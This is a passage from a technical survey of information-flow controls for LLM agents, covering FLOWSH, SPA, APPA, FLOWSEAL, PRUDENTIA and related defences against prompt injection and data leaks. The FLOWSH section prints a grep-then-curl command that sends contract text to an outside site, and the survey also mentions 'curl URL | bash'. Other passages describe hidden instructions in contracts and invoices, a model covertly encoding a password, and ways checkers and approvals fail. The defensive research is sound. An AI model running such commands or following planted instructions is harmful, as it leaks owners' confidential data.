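Štorek and colleagues tested GIF on agents run by six models. GIF ranked tokens by their influence on each action, and the researchers counted how many of the top 50 belonged to planted instructions or private data. They measured how often this count was higher for a run with a violation than for one without. It was higher about 91% of the time on AgentDojo and 92% on MSB, both benchmarks of prompt injection. On AgentDAM, which tests whether browser agents disclose private information, the figure was only 75%, and for one model it was 61%. GIF was therefore much weaker at detecting leaked secrets than at detecting injections, even though the researchers knew in advance which tokens were secret.

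GIF also leaves the final decision to another language model, which receives the most influential passages and allows or denies the action. The proof doesn't cover that model's judgement. On AgentDojo and MSB, this method used 59% to 73% fewer tokens than having a model read the whole run, and was about as accurate.

### Reading the model's attention

Sightline examines attention, which lets a model draw on earlier tokens when it computes a new one. In the usual kind of language model, only attention moves information from one position in the text to another. Xu and colleagues proved in Lean that if no chain of attention leads from a passage to the output, small changes to the passage can't affect the output.

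Checking whether a model attended to an input rarely shows whether it used that input, because models pay at least a little attention to almost everything. A model may also attend strongly to a passage it doesn't use, or base its answer on one it barely attends to. Sightline therefore learns from labelled examples which patterns of attention indicate that the model used an input. It then scores each input and drops the label of any that falls below a threshold.

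The researchers choose the threshold to limit how often Sightline drops a label that it should have kept. They take n groups of programs, draw one input from each that the output is known to have used, and sort these inputs by score. For a target miss rate α, the threshold is the k-th lowest score, where

k = ⌊α(n + 1)⌋.

With 1,000 groups and a target of 1%, k is 10. If a new program resembles the old ones, an input used in its output is equally likely to take any of the 1,001 places in the combined ranking. The chance that it falls below the threshold is then at most 10 in 1,001, or about 1%.

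Xu and colleagues tested this on prompts from 2,103 families of open-source programs. Sightline missed about 1% of the real flows and removed between 44% and 66% of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model. With the same target, GIF removed at most 12% of them. But only 12% to 14% of the inputs were unused, so Sightline removed roughly 5% to 9% of all labels.

They also replayed 120 steps from AgentDojo runs by an agent using a small open model. With a target of 5%, Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels, and a policy like that of FIDES still blocked all 34 calls that would have carried out an attack.

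### What a missed dependency costs

A 1% miss rate is an average over programs, so it is a poor guide to the risk for a particular secret. In a separate analysis of one model, Sightline missed 10% of the flows behind the model's most confident outputs when the threshold was set to miss 5% of flows overall. A developer can reduce this problem by setting a separate threshold for each level of confidence.

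The risk of losing a label also grows with the number of steps. If an agent uses a contract in 100 steps and each has an independent 1% chance of losing the label, the chance of at least one loss is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. The contract leaks only if the agent then sends the unlabelled text to someone who isn't allowed to read it, but later checks treat that text, and anything derived from it, as public.

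The threshold calculation assumes that new programs resemble the old ones, but an attacker can write text that violates this assumption. Also, in the reference labels, an input counts as used only if the output visibly reflects it. If a malicious model encoded a password in its choice of synonyms, the people or models labelling the examples would probably mark the password as unused, and Sightline would learn from the wrong label.

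If an unnecessary label stops the agent from posting a notice, Ann can post it herself, but a missing label can make a contract permanently public. The full join or a fresh answer from permitted documents therefore seems better for text that leaves the firm. Sightline's estimates are more suitable where a mistake would do less harm, such as in messages between colleagues.

### Keeping the text away from the model

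Hiding data in variables, as FIDES does, avoids having to work out which data the model used. If Hana's email never enters the context, the agent can still publish the notice about Friday.

The agent also can't reason about data hidden from it. It can put the hidden time of the hearing into the calendar, but it can't notice that the hearing clashes with another meeting and suggest moving one of them.

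Labels also accumulate inside the variables. If a quarantined model summarises 20 documents, the summary takes the join of all 20 labels, so perhaps only Ann may read it. This is less harmful than a restricted context because it affects only the summary and whatever the agent makes from it. A developer could reduce the harm further by having the quarantined model redo the summary using only the documents that the intended recipient may read.

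## Can flow control cover shells, databases and work over many sessions?

Most of the tools discussed so far have effects that a developer can describe in advance. `send_email` sends a message to the addresses in its arguments, so software can compare those addresses with the message's permitted readers before making the call. The effects of commands run in a shell, the program that runs typed commands, are much harder to predict. `python report.py` might add up some numbers, overwrite a settings file or upload a folder, depending on the script, the programs it starts and the files it finds. `curl URL | bash` downloads a program and runs it immediately, so even the code is unknown when the agent requests the call.

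A list of permitted commands, like TACIT's, can't show what a permitted command will do on a particular run. A cautious label system could treat all shell output as secret and untrusted and ask a person to approve every command, but that person might have to approve dozens of commands in a single task.

### Watching a command as it runs

In *FLOWSH*, Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026), several of whom also worked on FIDES, instead judge a command by the files it opens and the effects it tries to have. Their shell, FLOWSH, runs each command in a fresh sandbox connected to the outside only through files and a network proxy, a program that relays requests to other computers. A monitor in the operating system's kernel records every file opened by the command or by any program it starts.

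FLOWSH holds file changes in a temporary layer until the command ends, then applies them if the policy allows. Otherwise it asks the user to accept or reject all of them together, since applying only some could leave the files inconsistent. Network requests are irreversible, so the proxy checks each one before forwarding it. It refuses a forbidden request, and the agent can then ask the user to allow that destination in a new command. Even a request that only fetches a page counts as an effect, because its address can carry data.

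The whole command has one label:

ℓ<sub>sh</sub> = ℓ<sub>ctx</sub> ⊔ ℓ<sub>arg</sub> ⊔ ⨆<sub>f ∈ F</sub> ℓ(f) ⊔ ⨆<sub>e ∈ E</sub> ℓ(e)

Here ℓ<sub>ctx</sub> is the label of the agent's context, and ℓ<sub>arg</sub> covers any hidden variables in the command. F is the set of files the command has opened, and E is the set of network addresses it has connected to. The label includes the files because a command can use a file's contents without showing them to the agent.

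Suppose Ann's agent has just read a supplier's web page, so its context is untrusted and public. It then runs these two lines as a single command:

```
grep -i penalty contract.txt > clause.txt
curl --data-binary @clause.txt https://terms.example
```

The first line searches a contract and copies every line that mentions a penalty into a new file, and the second sends that file to a website. The contract is trusted and has the readers {Ann, Bob, Cem}.

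| Event | Label of the command | What FLOWSH does |
|---|---|---|
| The command starts | untrusted, everyone | takes the context's label |
| `grep` opens `contract.txt` | untrusted, {Ann, Bob, Cem} | adds the file's label |
| `grep` writes `clause.txt` | unchanged | holds the change back |
| `curl` tries to contact the site | unchanged | refuses, as the site isn't a permitted reader |
| The command ends | unchanged | saves `clause.txt` with this label |

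FLOWSH stores the label with the file, so the label survives a computer restart. If the agent opens `clause.txt` next week in a new conversation, the same restrictions apply.

Without the supplier's page, FLOWSH would have let the agent send the clause to the website. The policy that Kim and colleagues used, like the one in the FIDES tests, also permits a request if all the inputs so far are trusted. A firm can remove this exception, but its staff would then get more approval requests.

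### Fewer questions, and some lost work

Kim and colleagues tested FLOWSH with the model GPT-6.2 Sol on the 89 tasks of Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of difficult command-line work, and on 17 knowledge-work tasks of their own, such as planning a week from chat messages and a calendar. They also built 19 attack cases. In 11, the attacker tried to overwrite a file that would run code later, and in the other eight, the attacker tried to send private data out. The attacker controlled everything the model wrote once hostile text reached it, so the attacks didn't depend on fooling the model.

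In one setting, a simulated approver made no mistakes. "Approvals" in this table means approval requests per completed task:

| Defence | Knowledge tasks completed | Approvals | Terminal-Bench completed | Approvals |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Permissive sandbox | 96.1% | 6.7 | 77.5% | 9.7 |
| Sandbox with typical limits | 76.5% | 5.7 | 64.4% | 10.0 |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0 | 1.9% | 0 |
| Labels on the context only | 60.8% | 1.8 | 67.8% | 9.4 |
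| FLOWSH | 88.2% | 1.2 | 67.8% | 0.4 |

The permissive sandbox required 5.8 times as many approvals as FLOWSH per completed knowledge task, and 22.5 times as many on Terminal-Bench. FLOWSH's completion rate was 7.9 percentage points lower on the knowledge tasks and 9.7 points lower on Terminal-Bench. The choice of baseline makes the approval ratios look large, because the permissive sandbox required approval for every shell command, even one that only read a file.

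No attack succeeded under any defence in this setting. The strict sandbox blocked them automatically, and the other defences could rely on an approver who never allowed one. The setting without approvals tests the software better. There, FLOWSH stopped all 40 attacks that reached a model, while the permissive sandbox stopped none of 51. The sandbox with typical limits, which Kim and colleagues based on Claude Code's settings, let 3 of 39 through.

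FLOWSH completed 58.8% of the knowledge tasks without approvals, compared with 94.1% for the permissive sandbox. It completed all 18 runs that used only trusted data and all 6 that combined untrusted data with public data, but only 6 of the 27 that involved both untrusted and private data. Such work is common in an office; one of these tasks, for example, was to compare published papers with a private project.

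Some of FLOWSH's failed runs on Terminal-Bench had nothing to do with labels. With approvals available, 21 of its 86 failed runs needed a program to keep running after the command that started it ended, which FLOWSH doesn't allow. Another 44 were on tasks that the permissive sandbox never completed either. FLOWSH also made whole tasks take 17% to 34% longer.

### Whole files and whole commands

FLOWSH counts opening a file as reading all of it. If a long report has one confidential page, a command that extracts only the report's public summary still gets the confidential label. A program that opens the report but reads nothing gets the label too.

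Using one label for the whole command also restricts some files more than necessary. Suppose a command counts the words in a public newsletter, saves the number in `count.txt`, and then counts the words in a contract. FLOWSH labels saved files only after the command ends and ignores the order of reads and writes, so `count.txt` becomes as restricted as the contract, even though it contains nothing from the contract. The agent could avoid this by running two commands, with the newsletter first.

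Websites have a similar problem, because FLOWSH gives each network address a single label. GitHub serves both a firm's own code and strangers' bug reports, so a cautious firm has to label everything from it as untrusted.

These rules are cautious, but they contribute to label creep. More precise tracking would have to follow data inside each program, which requires separate tools for each programming language and can slow the programs down. Recording the order in which a command opens files would be a smaller change and would fix the newsletter example.

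### Results that an agent keeps for later

Agents also keep notes and earlier results outside ordinary files. In *SPA*, Girrens and Wang (2026) give an example in which a user asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice and remember its details, then tells it on Tuesday to pay the invoice. If an attacker has altered the invoice, a hidden instruction could reach the agent's planner on Tuesday. Even without a hidden instruction, a false account number could misdirect the payment.

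*Trojan Hippo Bench* (2026) sets out a simple defence for agent memory. Any note written after the agent has read text that an attacker could control gets a permanent label, and a session that retrieves the note can no longer send data out. Deciding how much to label is difficult. *AgentKernel* (2026) notes that if a whole session shares one label, a single untrusted web excerpt makes most of that session's memory unusable. Labelling each note separately is more practical, but the software has to work out which sources each note came from, and an attacker can write text that makes it misidentify them.

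SPA avoids that guess because a fixed program determines which inputs go into each result. It handles each request as follows:

1. The planner writes a complete plan before any tool runs. It sees the request and descriptions of earlier results, but not the results themselves.
2. A checker works through the plan, computes the label of every value and compares it with the limits of each tool that would receive it.
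3. If any call would break a limit, SPA rejects the plan and nothing runs.
4. Otherwise, an interpreter runs the plan exactly as written and stores each result with its label and a description.

The planner writes the descriptions before the tools run, so a hostile invoice can't affect them. On Tuesday, the planner sees that an "invoice from Acme" exists and writes a step to retrieve it. The account number comes back with its untrusted label, and the checker rejects the payment if the payment tool requires trusted data.

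The checker also examines both branches of every condition, which closes the gap that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL. SPA never sends the planner the reason for a rejection or requests another plan, so it has no retry loop that could leak secrets. But this also means a single badly written plan ends the request.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo with the small model GPT-5.4 nano. They also split each of the benchmark's 97 tasks into two to five successive requests to test whether the agent could reuse earlier results.

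| Test | Tasks completed, no label checks | With checks | Attacks succeeding, no checks | With checks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| One request | 53.0% | 29.0% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Several requests | 62.5% | 35.3% | 0.3% | 0.2% |

The checks nearly halved the number of completed tasks. They had few attacks left to stop, because keeping tool results away from the planner had already defeated most of them. The remaining attack success rate of 0.2% may overstate the danger, since it amounts to about two runs, and Girrens and Wang describe two runs that the benchmark counted as successful attacks although SPA had rejected the plan.

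The results provide little evidence about delayed attacks, because attacks succeeded in only 0.6% of runs even when Girrens and Wang let later planners read the stored values without label checks. They acknowledge that the benchmark's attacks are a weak test of poisoned memory.

With results stored this way and the checks on, later plans retrieved the right earlier result in 89.9% of the cases where it existed. Most of the lost work came from the integrity rule, which rejects the genuine invoice along with the forged one.

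### Tools without labels

SPA and FIDES rely on a description of every tool, which a firm that connects an agent to dozens of existing services may not have. APPA (Agentic Permissions Policy Algebra; Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) lets such a firm start with some tools unlabelled.

When an unlabelled tool returns data, APPA records the data's label as unknown. The agent can keep working with the data, and APPA carries a list of unknown sources along with the ordinary label. APPA tries to determine the unknown label only when the agent attempts an action that depends on it, such as sending an email whose recipient must be a permitted reader. It then runs a function, called a cast, that the firm has registered to classify data from that source. Each cast has a limit on how permissive a label it may assign. If the firm has registered no suitable cast, or the cast fails, APPA blocks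 the action.

APPA also predicts how each call will change the context's label. One test tool reads a confidential document and emails it in a single call. APPA adds the tool's declared label to the context's label before the tool runs, and so blocks the email. A system that checked only the context's current label would allow it, because the agent hasn't read anything confidential yet. APPA checks again after a tool runs, in case it has returned something more restricted than its description declared.

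### Continuing after a refusal

In most label systems, a refusal leaves the agent to find another way by itself. Reading more data can't help, since it never loosens the context's label. APPA therefore searches the firm's rules for permitted ways forward and gives the agent a list. Depending on the problem, the agent might be able to:

- complete a required earlier step, such as logging a contract before sending it
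- have approved software remove the sensitive parts
- request permission for that exact call
- do the reading in a separate branch

The last option works much like `fork` in the LLMbda calculus. The branch starts with a copy of the conversation and its label. For example, it can read a stranger's bug report and return only a ticket number, a severity chosen from a list and a component name. It can't return free text, so an instruction in the report never reaches the main conversation. APPA then discards the branch.

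A hostile report can still make the branch choose the wrong severity, because checking the form of an answer doesn't ensure that it's true. The firm has to decide whether to trust such answers. Discarding a branch doesn't undo any email it has sent.

Kravchenko and colleagues built Bench-Corp, a benchmark of 20 multi-step office scenarios. They tested three models, running each scenario five times under each of two sets of instructions, one of which encouraged the model to follow orders it found in data. APPA completed 88.0% to 90.0% of the 200 runs per model, and no attack succeeded in any of the 600 runs. With the checks off, the same agent completed 90.0% to 92.5% of runs, and attacks succeeded in 30.0% to 35.5%.

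With GPT-5.6 Luna, APPA completed 88.0% of runs, compared with 56.5% without branches and 35.0% without the suggested remedies. No attack succeeded in any of these versions, so these recovery options didn't weaken security in the test.

Bench-Corp favours APPA because its designers wrote the scenarios to exercise APPA's features. APPA did less well on AgentThreatBench, an existing benchmark of 24 tasks. It again allowed no attacks in 720 runs, but it completed only 64.2% to 76.7% of tasks, depending on the model and instructions, which was 14 to 28 percentage points below an unprotected agent. Kravchenko and colleagues also report much worse results for FIDES than for APPA on Bench-Corp, but the FIDES policies they wrote left out several of the benchmark's rules, such as exactly who may receive a document.

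### When a database combines people's records

A label that follows the data can be too strict for statistics. Suppose a firm may publish figures about its users' receipts only if each figure combines data from at least two users. If each receipt's label allows only its owner to read it, an average over many users has no permitted readers, although it may be the safest figure to publish.

Access control can't express this rule either. Consider three receipts:

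| User | Category | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Ann | travel | 40 |
| Bob | travel | 200 |
| Ann | meals | 60 |

An agent asks for the average cost in each category. The travel average, 120, combines two users, so the firm may publish it. The meals average, 60, comes only from Ann's receipt, so it reveals what she spent.

Row-level access control decides which rows the agent may read, but whether the firm may use a row depends on which other rows the query combines it with. The agent must read Ann's travel receipt to compute the travel average, but once it can read that row, it can also publish it. Hiding Ann's meals receipt would suppress the meals average, but it would also spoil the overall average of 100, which combines both users.

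Summers and Wu (2026), in *Data Flow Control*, write the rule about the result instead:

```
SOURCE Receipts
CONSTRAINT COUNT(DISTINCT Receipts.uid) > 1
ON FAIL REMOVE
```

The rule counts the different users (`uid`) whose receipts contributed to each row of a query's result, and removes any row with only one user. It therefore keeps the travel average and drops the meals average. If the agent asks for individual receipts, it gets nothing.

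Databases can record which input rows produced each result, but this can make a query thousands of times slower. Summers and Wu's software instead adds the check to the query before the database runs it. For the category averages, the new query is in effect:

```
SELECT category, AVG(cost) FROM Receipts
GROUP BY category
HAVING COUNT(DISTINCT uid) > 1
```

The last line is the addition. Across five database systems, the average extra time on a standard set of queries was about zero.

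The same language can require every expense an agent enters to come from a real receipt, or limit the deductible share of a meal to 50%. These rules work even if the agent doesn't understand them, and enforcing them doesn't require a language model.

The method covers only one query at a time, so it doesn't prevent a well-known attack on published statistics. An agent could ask for the total spending of Ann, Bob and Cem, and then for that of Bob and Cem. Both totals satisfy the rule, but subtracting the second from the first gives Ann's spending. Raising the minimum number of users would block this pair of queries, but the same attack works with larger groups.

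An agent could also copy the receipts into another table and publish from there. The software's rules do not yet follow data through intermediate tables or across several agent turns, which DAPLab, the Columbia University group behind the software, lists as future work. The current version also does not cover some queries, including those that use negation, such as a search for users who have no receipts.

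### Missing and wrong labels

Each of these systems depends on people having described the data or the tools correctly, but they treat gaps in those descriptions differently:

| System | What the firm must trust | What happens without a label or rule |
|---|---|---|
| FLOWSH | the sandbox, monitor, proxy and settings, and programs outside the sandbox | the file gets a default label |
| SPA | the checker, the interpreter and each tool's limits | the checker rejects a plan that retrieves the result |
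| APPA | tool descriptions, casts and approved data-cleaning software | work continues until an action needs the label |
| Data flow control | the rules, the query rewriter and columns such as `uid` | the query runs without restriction |

Kim and colleagues set FLOWSH's default file label to untrusted and readable only by the user. If the monitor misses a file access, FLOWSH gives the command the strictest label. Both choices are safer than the default in Microsoft's Agent Framework, which treats unlabelled sources as trusted and public. But a strict default makes more work for the administrator. Running a program counts as reading its file, so an unlabelled copy of `grep` would make every command that used it untrusted.

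In *Please Don't Kill My Vibe*, Summers, Mohammed and Wu (2025) suggest a cautious default for databases too, in which every row written by a user or agent is marked unsafe for prompts until a check clears it.

A wrong label is harder to deal with than a missing one, because the software treats it as correct. If the label is too strict, somebody will probably notice that the agent can't finish a task, but if it is too permissive, the agent works normally and the data can leak without warning. In the database, one person with two accounts would count as two users, and the rule would release that person's receipts as if they were a group average.

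Firms may use language models to write labels because so many are needed. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026) compared the labels that OpenAI's o1 gave to tools with those from human annotators. The agreement was 0.95 on a scale where 1 is perfect and 0 is what chance would produce. But o1 rated a tool that opens web pages as low in sensitivity, while the humans rated it moderate because it could help with phishing. High agreement overall does not rule out such errors, and an attacker needs only one. The paper recommends that people review the model's labels.

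Attackers may also try to change labels. FLOWSH removes any label that a command writes and substitutes its own, but programs outside the sandbox can still alter labels. *MemLineage* (2026) points out that anyone who can write to an agent's memory undetected can relabel its entries, unless the system protects the labels cryptographically.

Correcting a wrong label may not be enough, even if nothing has leaked yet. Suppose an administrator discovers that `contract.txt` was marked public by mistake and corrects the label. FLOWSH saved `clause.txt` with a label computed from the contract's old one, and the correction doesn't change the label on `clause.txt`. The administrator would have to find and relabel every file that drew on the contract.

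## Who may release protected data, and how often must a person decide?

Strict rules on data flow would forbid some of the work people want agents to do. A firm eventually has to show a contract to the other party, and a payroll agent has to tell the bank what to pay each employee. Even a login page violates noninterference, because rejecting a guess reveals that the password is something else. A useful system therefore needs exceptions, and its safety depends on the rules for making them.

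### Declassification and endorsement

An authorised person declassifies data by lowering its confidentiality label, as Ann does when she adds Dana to the readers of a contract summary. Endorsement is an authorised decision to treat untrusted data as trusted, as when Ann checks an invoice and tells the agent to act on it.

Endorsing data as reliable and letting more people read it are separate decisions. Endorsing an invoice doesn't let anyone else read it, and Dana may be allowed to read a summary that is still untrusted. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, the `endorse` operation can remove an untrusted label but not a secret one.

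A rule against releasing data offers little protection if an attacker can trigger its exceptions. Robust declassification permits a release only when no untrusted input influenced the decision to make it. Costa and colleagues' email rule for FIDES is an example, because data can reach someone who isn't a permitted reader only if the planner's context was trusted when it decided to send the data. The LLMbda calculus restricts endorsement similarly. If a program reaches `endorse` inside a branch that depends on untrusted data, the result stays untrusted.

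A trusted decision to send a message can still release the wrong text. Suppose Ann asks an agent to compare a supplier's draft contract with the firm's confidential price list and send the supplier a list of errors in the draft. A quarantined model reads both documents and follows a hidden instruction in the draft to quote the price list. The planner chose to send the email before seeing any untrusted text, so a check on that decision alone would allow the email, and the supplier would get the prices.

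Requiring the message to be trusted too would stop this email, but it would also block an honest list of errors.

### What, who, where and when

Sabelfeld and Sands (2009), in *Declassification: Dimensions and Principles*, sorted release policies by what they release, who controls the release, where in the system it happens and when. A firm's rule for a contract might cover all four:

| Dimension | Example |
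|---|---|
| What | the notice period, but not the price |
| Who | only the lawyer responsible for the contract |
| Where | only through the upload page for that client |
| When | only after both parties have signed |

A rule that leaves out one of these restrictions can allow a leak that the restriction would have prevented. If the firm specifies only who may release a contract, someone could trick the lawyer into sending the whole document to a competitor. If it specifies only what may be released, such as the notice period, that information could reach the competitor before anyone has signed.

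### Releasing only a small answer

A firm can also limit how much information a release contains. In FIDES, the planner can query a quarantined model about a hidden variable and specify the form of the answer, such as yes or no, one of several options, or free text. FIDES enforces that form with constrained decoding, which prevents the model from producing any token that would break it.

FIDES adds the form to the answer's label. Costa and colleagues order the forms by how much information they can carry:

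yes or no ⊑ choice from a list ⊑ free text

A policy might let an untrusted yes-or-no answer influence a payment but reject an untrusted sentence, because a yes or no is too short to contain a hidden instruction or a contract clause. Such a policy could also release a yes-or-no answer about a secret document while keeping the document secret.

If a question has *n* possible answers, one answer carries at most log₂ *n* bits. A yes-or-no answer carries at most 1 bit, and a choice of three carries at most about 1.58 bits. The average can be lower. An observer who is already 90% sure that a contract has no penalty clause learns only about 0.47 bits on average from being told whether it has one. If the agent can see that a yes-or-no query failed, failure is a third possible outcome, which raises the limit to about 1.58 bits.

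The limits on how much each answer can leak add up. As with timing leaks, 128 yes-or-no answers could reveal a 128-bit key. Fourteen could reveal a four-digit PIN, because they can distinguish 2¹⁴ (16,384) values and a PIN has only 10,000.

The types in FIDES's labels don't show how many answers a value was computed from. Under Costa and colleagues' join rule, a value computed from two or even 128 yes-or-no answers can still have the yes-or-no type. A separate counter would have to track how many bits of each secret have been released across all conversations and agents, since an agent could otherwise ask half the questions today and the rest tomorrow. It would also have to treat copies of a secret as the same secret.

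Repeated answers matter for integrity too. If a policy accepts one untrusted yes-or-no answer, an attacker who controls it can choose between two courses of action. Ten such answers could let the attacker choose among up to 1,024.

### Permissions and fixed rules

In TACIT's design, whoever holds the `CanAccess` permission decides whether to release a contract. But `reveal` returns an ordinary value, which code can then send anywhere. Odersky and colleagues leave run-time checks on releases to future work.

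A fixed rule puts the decision in ordinary code. In the scheme that *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) proposes, a model that has read untrusted text may suggest a value, such as a file path or a time interval. The value stays untrusted until a fixed program has done three things:

1. It converts the value to a standard form.
2. It compares the value with trusted records and the policy, and rejects even a well-formed path if the policy forbids it.
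3. It issues a release that is valid for one field of one action, and records where the value came from and which code approved it.

A free-text explanation doesn't qualify, however convincing it is. The paper calls this process declassification, but the labels being changed concern trust, so most of the process would usually be called endorsement.

A fixed rule can be immune to persuasive language. But someone has to write it in advance, and it is hard to write a program that decides whether a paragraph about a contract reveals too much.

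### Asking another model

Language models can attempt such judgements. Štorek and colleagues tested four of them on GIF's final decision, showing each model only the one to three passages that had most influenced an action.

The checkers scored 0.97 to 1.22 times as high as the same models reading the whole run. The smallest model, Qwen 3 8B, gained the most. On two prompt-injection benchmarks, it matched GPT-5.5 reading the whole run when given three passages, at less than an eightieth of the cost. On AgentDAM, the privacy benchmark, selecting passages saved only 19% to 24% of the tokens, because the agent's history was already short.

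These ratios compare one fallible judge with another, so a firm can't use them to determine how often a checker would release a secret. Štorek and colleagues leave it to future work to define formally what the checker should permit.

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FLOWSEAL, which combines a model-based checker with ordinary software to protect an agent that holds someone's private records and communicates with outsiders. Software outside the agent's context tracks which records the agent has read and intercepts everything it tries to write or share. If the recipient isn't authorised, the software sends the protected records and the proposed message to a separate model, which must answer SAFE or BLOCKED. The agent can't skip this check, even if an outsider fools it.

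The researchers devised three attacks that use ordinary requests to make a disclosure look like harmless work. These attacks leaked 44% to 76% of the sensitive items against an earlier defence that relied on instructions to the agent, and 0.5% to 2.3% against FLOWSEAL. Across all eight attack types in the study, the leak rate was between 0% and 3.3%.

FLOWSEAL completed 72.4% of harmless requests, close to the best alternative's 75.9%, but it did much worse when it was supposed to release data. In one test, the owner of the records would consent to a legitimate release if the agent asked. FLOWSEAL's agent asked less often than agents with four other defences, and it released only 32.7% of the items, while they released 61% to 86%.

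To find out how much the checker contributed, the researchers replaced its answers with a fixed one. These results are for one of the new attacks:

| Checker | Sensitive items leaked | Harmless requests completed |
|---|---|---|
| Working normally | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always answers BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |
| Always answers SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |

In this test, no recipient had authorisation in advance and the owners ignored requests for it, so an agent whose checker always blocked could do nothing useful. The balance between leaks and completed work therefore depended almost entirely on the checker's judgement.

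The 1.3% in the second row is odd, because nothing should leak if the checker blocks every message. Either the model that scored the runs made some mistakes or a little data got out by another route. Differences of about one percentage point in this study are therefore hard to interpret.

### From a guarantee to an estimate

Shim and colleagues prove that FLOWSEAL lets an agent send content derived from a protected record to an unauthorised recipient only if the checker wrongly answers SAFE. This holds because every outgoing message passes through the interceptor. Once the agent has read a protected record, everything it writes has a restricted label, and only the checker can then release a message.

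The theorem thus reduces the security of the whole system to the checker's error rate. Researchers have to estimate that rate from examples because no proof gives it, and an attacker can look for different examples. Paraphrases of a record caused most of the checker's errors, and Shim and colleagues warn that a fact split across several messages might also get through. Checking each message separately has the same weakness as limiting each answer separately.

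An attacker can also try repeatedly. If each attempt had an independent 3.3% chance of success, about 21 attempts would give an even chance of at least one leak. The true rate might also be higher, because the researchers excluded prompt injection from their study, and a real attacker could try to influence the text that the checker reads.

A model's errors do less harm if the model can block a release or refer it to a person but can't approve it. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) gives classifiers this limited role in decisions about releasing data. A mistaken block causes some delay, and if a classifier misses a danger, the system's other controls still decide whether to release the data.

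### One approval for one message

Agent libOS is software for running agents that keep their memory and tools over long periods. Some recipients may receive highly sensitive data only if a person approves the exact release. Each approval is tied to:

- the agent that will send the data
- the recipient
- the exact content
- the versions and labels of the sources
- the current task's permissions and the current list of recipients.

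Suppose Ann approves emailing Dana a particular summary. The approval becomes invalid if the agent changes a word, chooses another recipient or draws on a newer version of the contract. The software uses up the approval when it sends the email, so the agent can't send it twice. If the system crashes during sending and can't tell whether the email went out, it records the result as unknown and does not automatically try again.

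The contracts keep their original labels, so Ann's approval has no effect on later messages. Her approval also doesn't endorse any data, so an action that requires trusted data still fails when the data is untrusted, even if she has approved the recipient. The software can't stop Dana from forwarding the summary.

With such a narrow approval, Ann can see exactly what she is permitting. But if an agent has to send different summaries to 50 suppliers, she may have to approve 50 emails.

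### Asking for fewer approvals

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* describes PRUDENTIA, the successor to FIDES, which tries to reduce the number of decisions a person must make. Its planner has access to the policies and the context's current label. Before revealing a hidden variable, the planner must write a plan that explains why it needs the text and lists the calls it expects to make afterwards.

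The planner can then either reveal the text and accept an untrusted context, or ask the user to endorse the text first. If the user agrees, the context stays trusted.

The paper gives the example of an email that lists ten tasks, each requiring a restricted tool. If the planner reads the email without endorsement, the user has to approve ten calls, whereas endorsing the email takes one decision. But if the agent only has to read the email and answer a question, it needs no restricted tools, so asking for endorsement would waste the user's time.

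Endorsing the email also permits more actions than approving a single call. If an attacker has added an eleventh task to the list, a user who endorses the email without noticing the addition permits that task too. A user who approved each call separately would have another chance to notice it.

PRUDENTIA has no equivalent for declassification. Its designers thought that whether to share private data depends too much on the situation, so the user has to approve each call that would share it.

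### How to count approvals

The paper introduces two measures. Let *v*(τ) be the number of calls in a run τ that don't comply with the policy and so need a person's approval. The human-in-the-loop (HITL) load is the sum of *v*(τ) over all completed tasks. The task completion rate with at most *k* approvals, written TCR@*k*, is

TCR@*k* = (number of tasks completed with *v*(τ) ≤ *k*) ÷ (number of tasks).

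TCR@0 counts only tasks that the agent completes without help, and TCR@∞ allows unlimited approvals.

Suppose two agents attempt the same five tasks. The first has no flow control and asks a person for approval before every consequential action, as many commercial agents do by default. The second asks only when an action fails a label check.

| Task | Approvals, no flow control | Approvals, flow control |
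|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0 | 0 |
| 2 | 1 | 0 |
| 3 | 2 | 0 |
| 4 | 3 | 1 |
| 5 | not completed | not completed |

Each agent completes 80% of the tasks with unlimited approvals. Without approvals, the first completes 20% and the second 60%. The human-in-the-loop (HITL) load is 6 for the first and 1 for the second.

Earlier studies of FIDES and CaMeL compared the protected agent's TCR@0 with the unprotected agent's TCR@∞. In this example, that comparison would be 60% against 80%, suggesting that flow control lowers TCR by 20 points. This is misleading because the unprotected agent is allowed unlimited approvals and the protected agent none. When both are allowed the same number, the protected agent in this example does at least as well.

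The older comparison is still relevant to a firm that would otherwise let an unprotected agent act without approvals. Such a firm would complete fewer tasks with FIDES, although the unprotected agent would be exposed to attacks.

### What PRUDENTIA achieved

On AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini model, the agents completed these shares of the tasks without any approvals:

| Agent | TCR@0 |
|---|---|
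| No flow control | 24.3% |
| Label checks only | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 59.1% |

PRUDENTIA led FIDES by 9 percentage points, the largest lead the paper reports in its main comparison. With the more capable GPT-5, it led by nearly 16 points.

PRUDENTIA also needed up to 1.9 times fewer approvals than FIDES. With o4-mini, its load was 19.2 approvals, compared with 36.8 for FIDES. When approvals were unlimited, it completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2%, compared with 75.7%). The load counts only completed tasks, so an agent can lower it by failing tasks that need many approvals. This effect explains little of the difference, because PRUDENTIA needed about 0.27 approvals per completed task and FIDES about 0.50.

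The researchers also tested PRUDENTIA on WASP, a benchmark that places prompt injections on simulated GitLab and Reddit sites. In 84 test cases with each of four models, PRUDENTIA needed no approvals, and no attack succeeded. An ordinary agent needed an average of 1 to 3.65 approvals per task, and 15% to 61% of the attacks diverted it from its task, depending on the model and site.

In the WASP tasks, the agent only had to post a comment or upvote a post, which it could do without reading any untrusted text. The researchers say FIDES performs similarly on these tasks. The result is therefore good evidence for hiding untrusted text, but not for PRUDENTIA's planning or its requests for endorsement.

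All these figures, like the savings Kim and colleagues found with FLOWSH, come from simulated approvals. The AgentDojo tests assumed that a person would approve every harmless request and stop every attack.

### How carefully people approve

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accept 93% of permission prompts in Claude Code. A later Anthropic article, *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), puts the figure at 97%. Anthropic attributes this partly to approval fatigue, meaning that users grow tired of the prompts.

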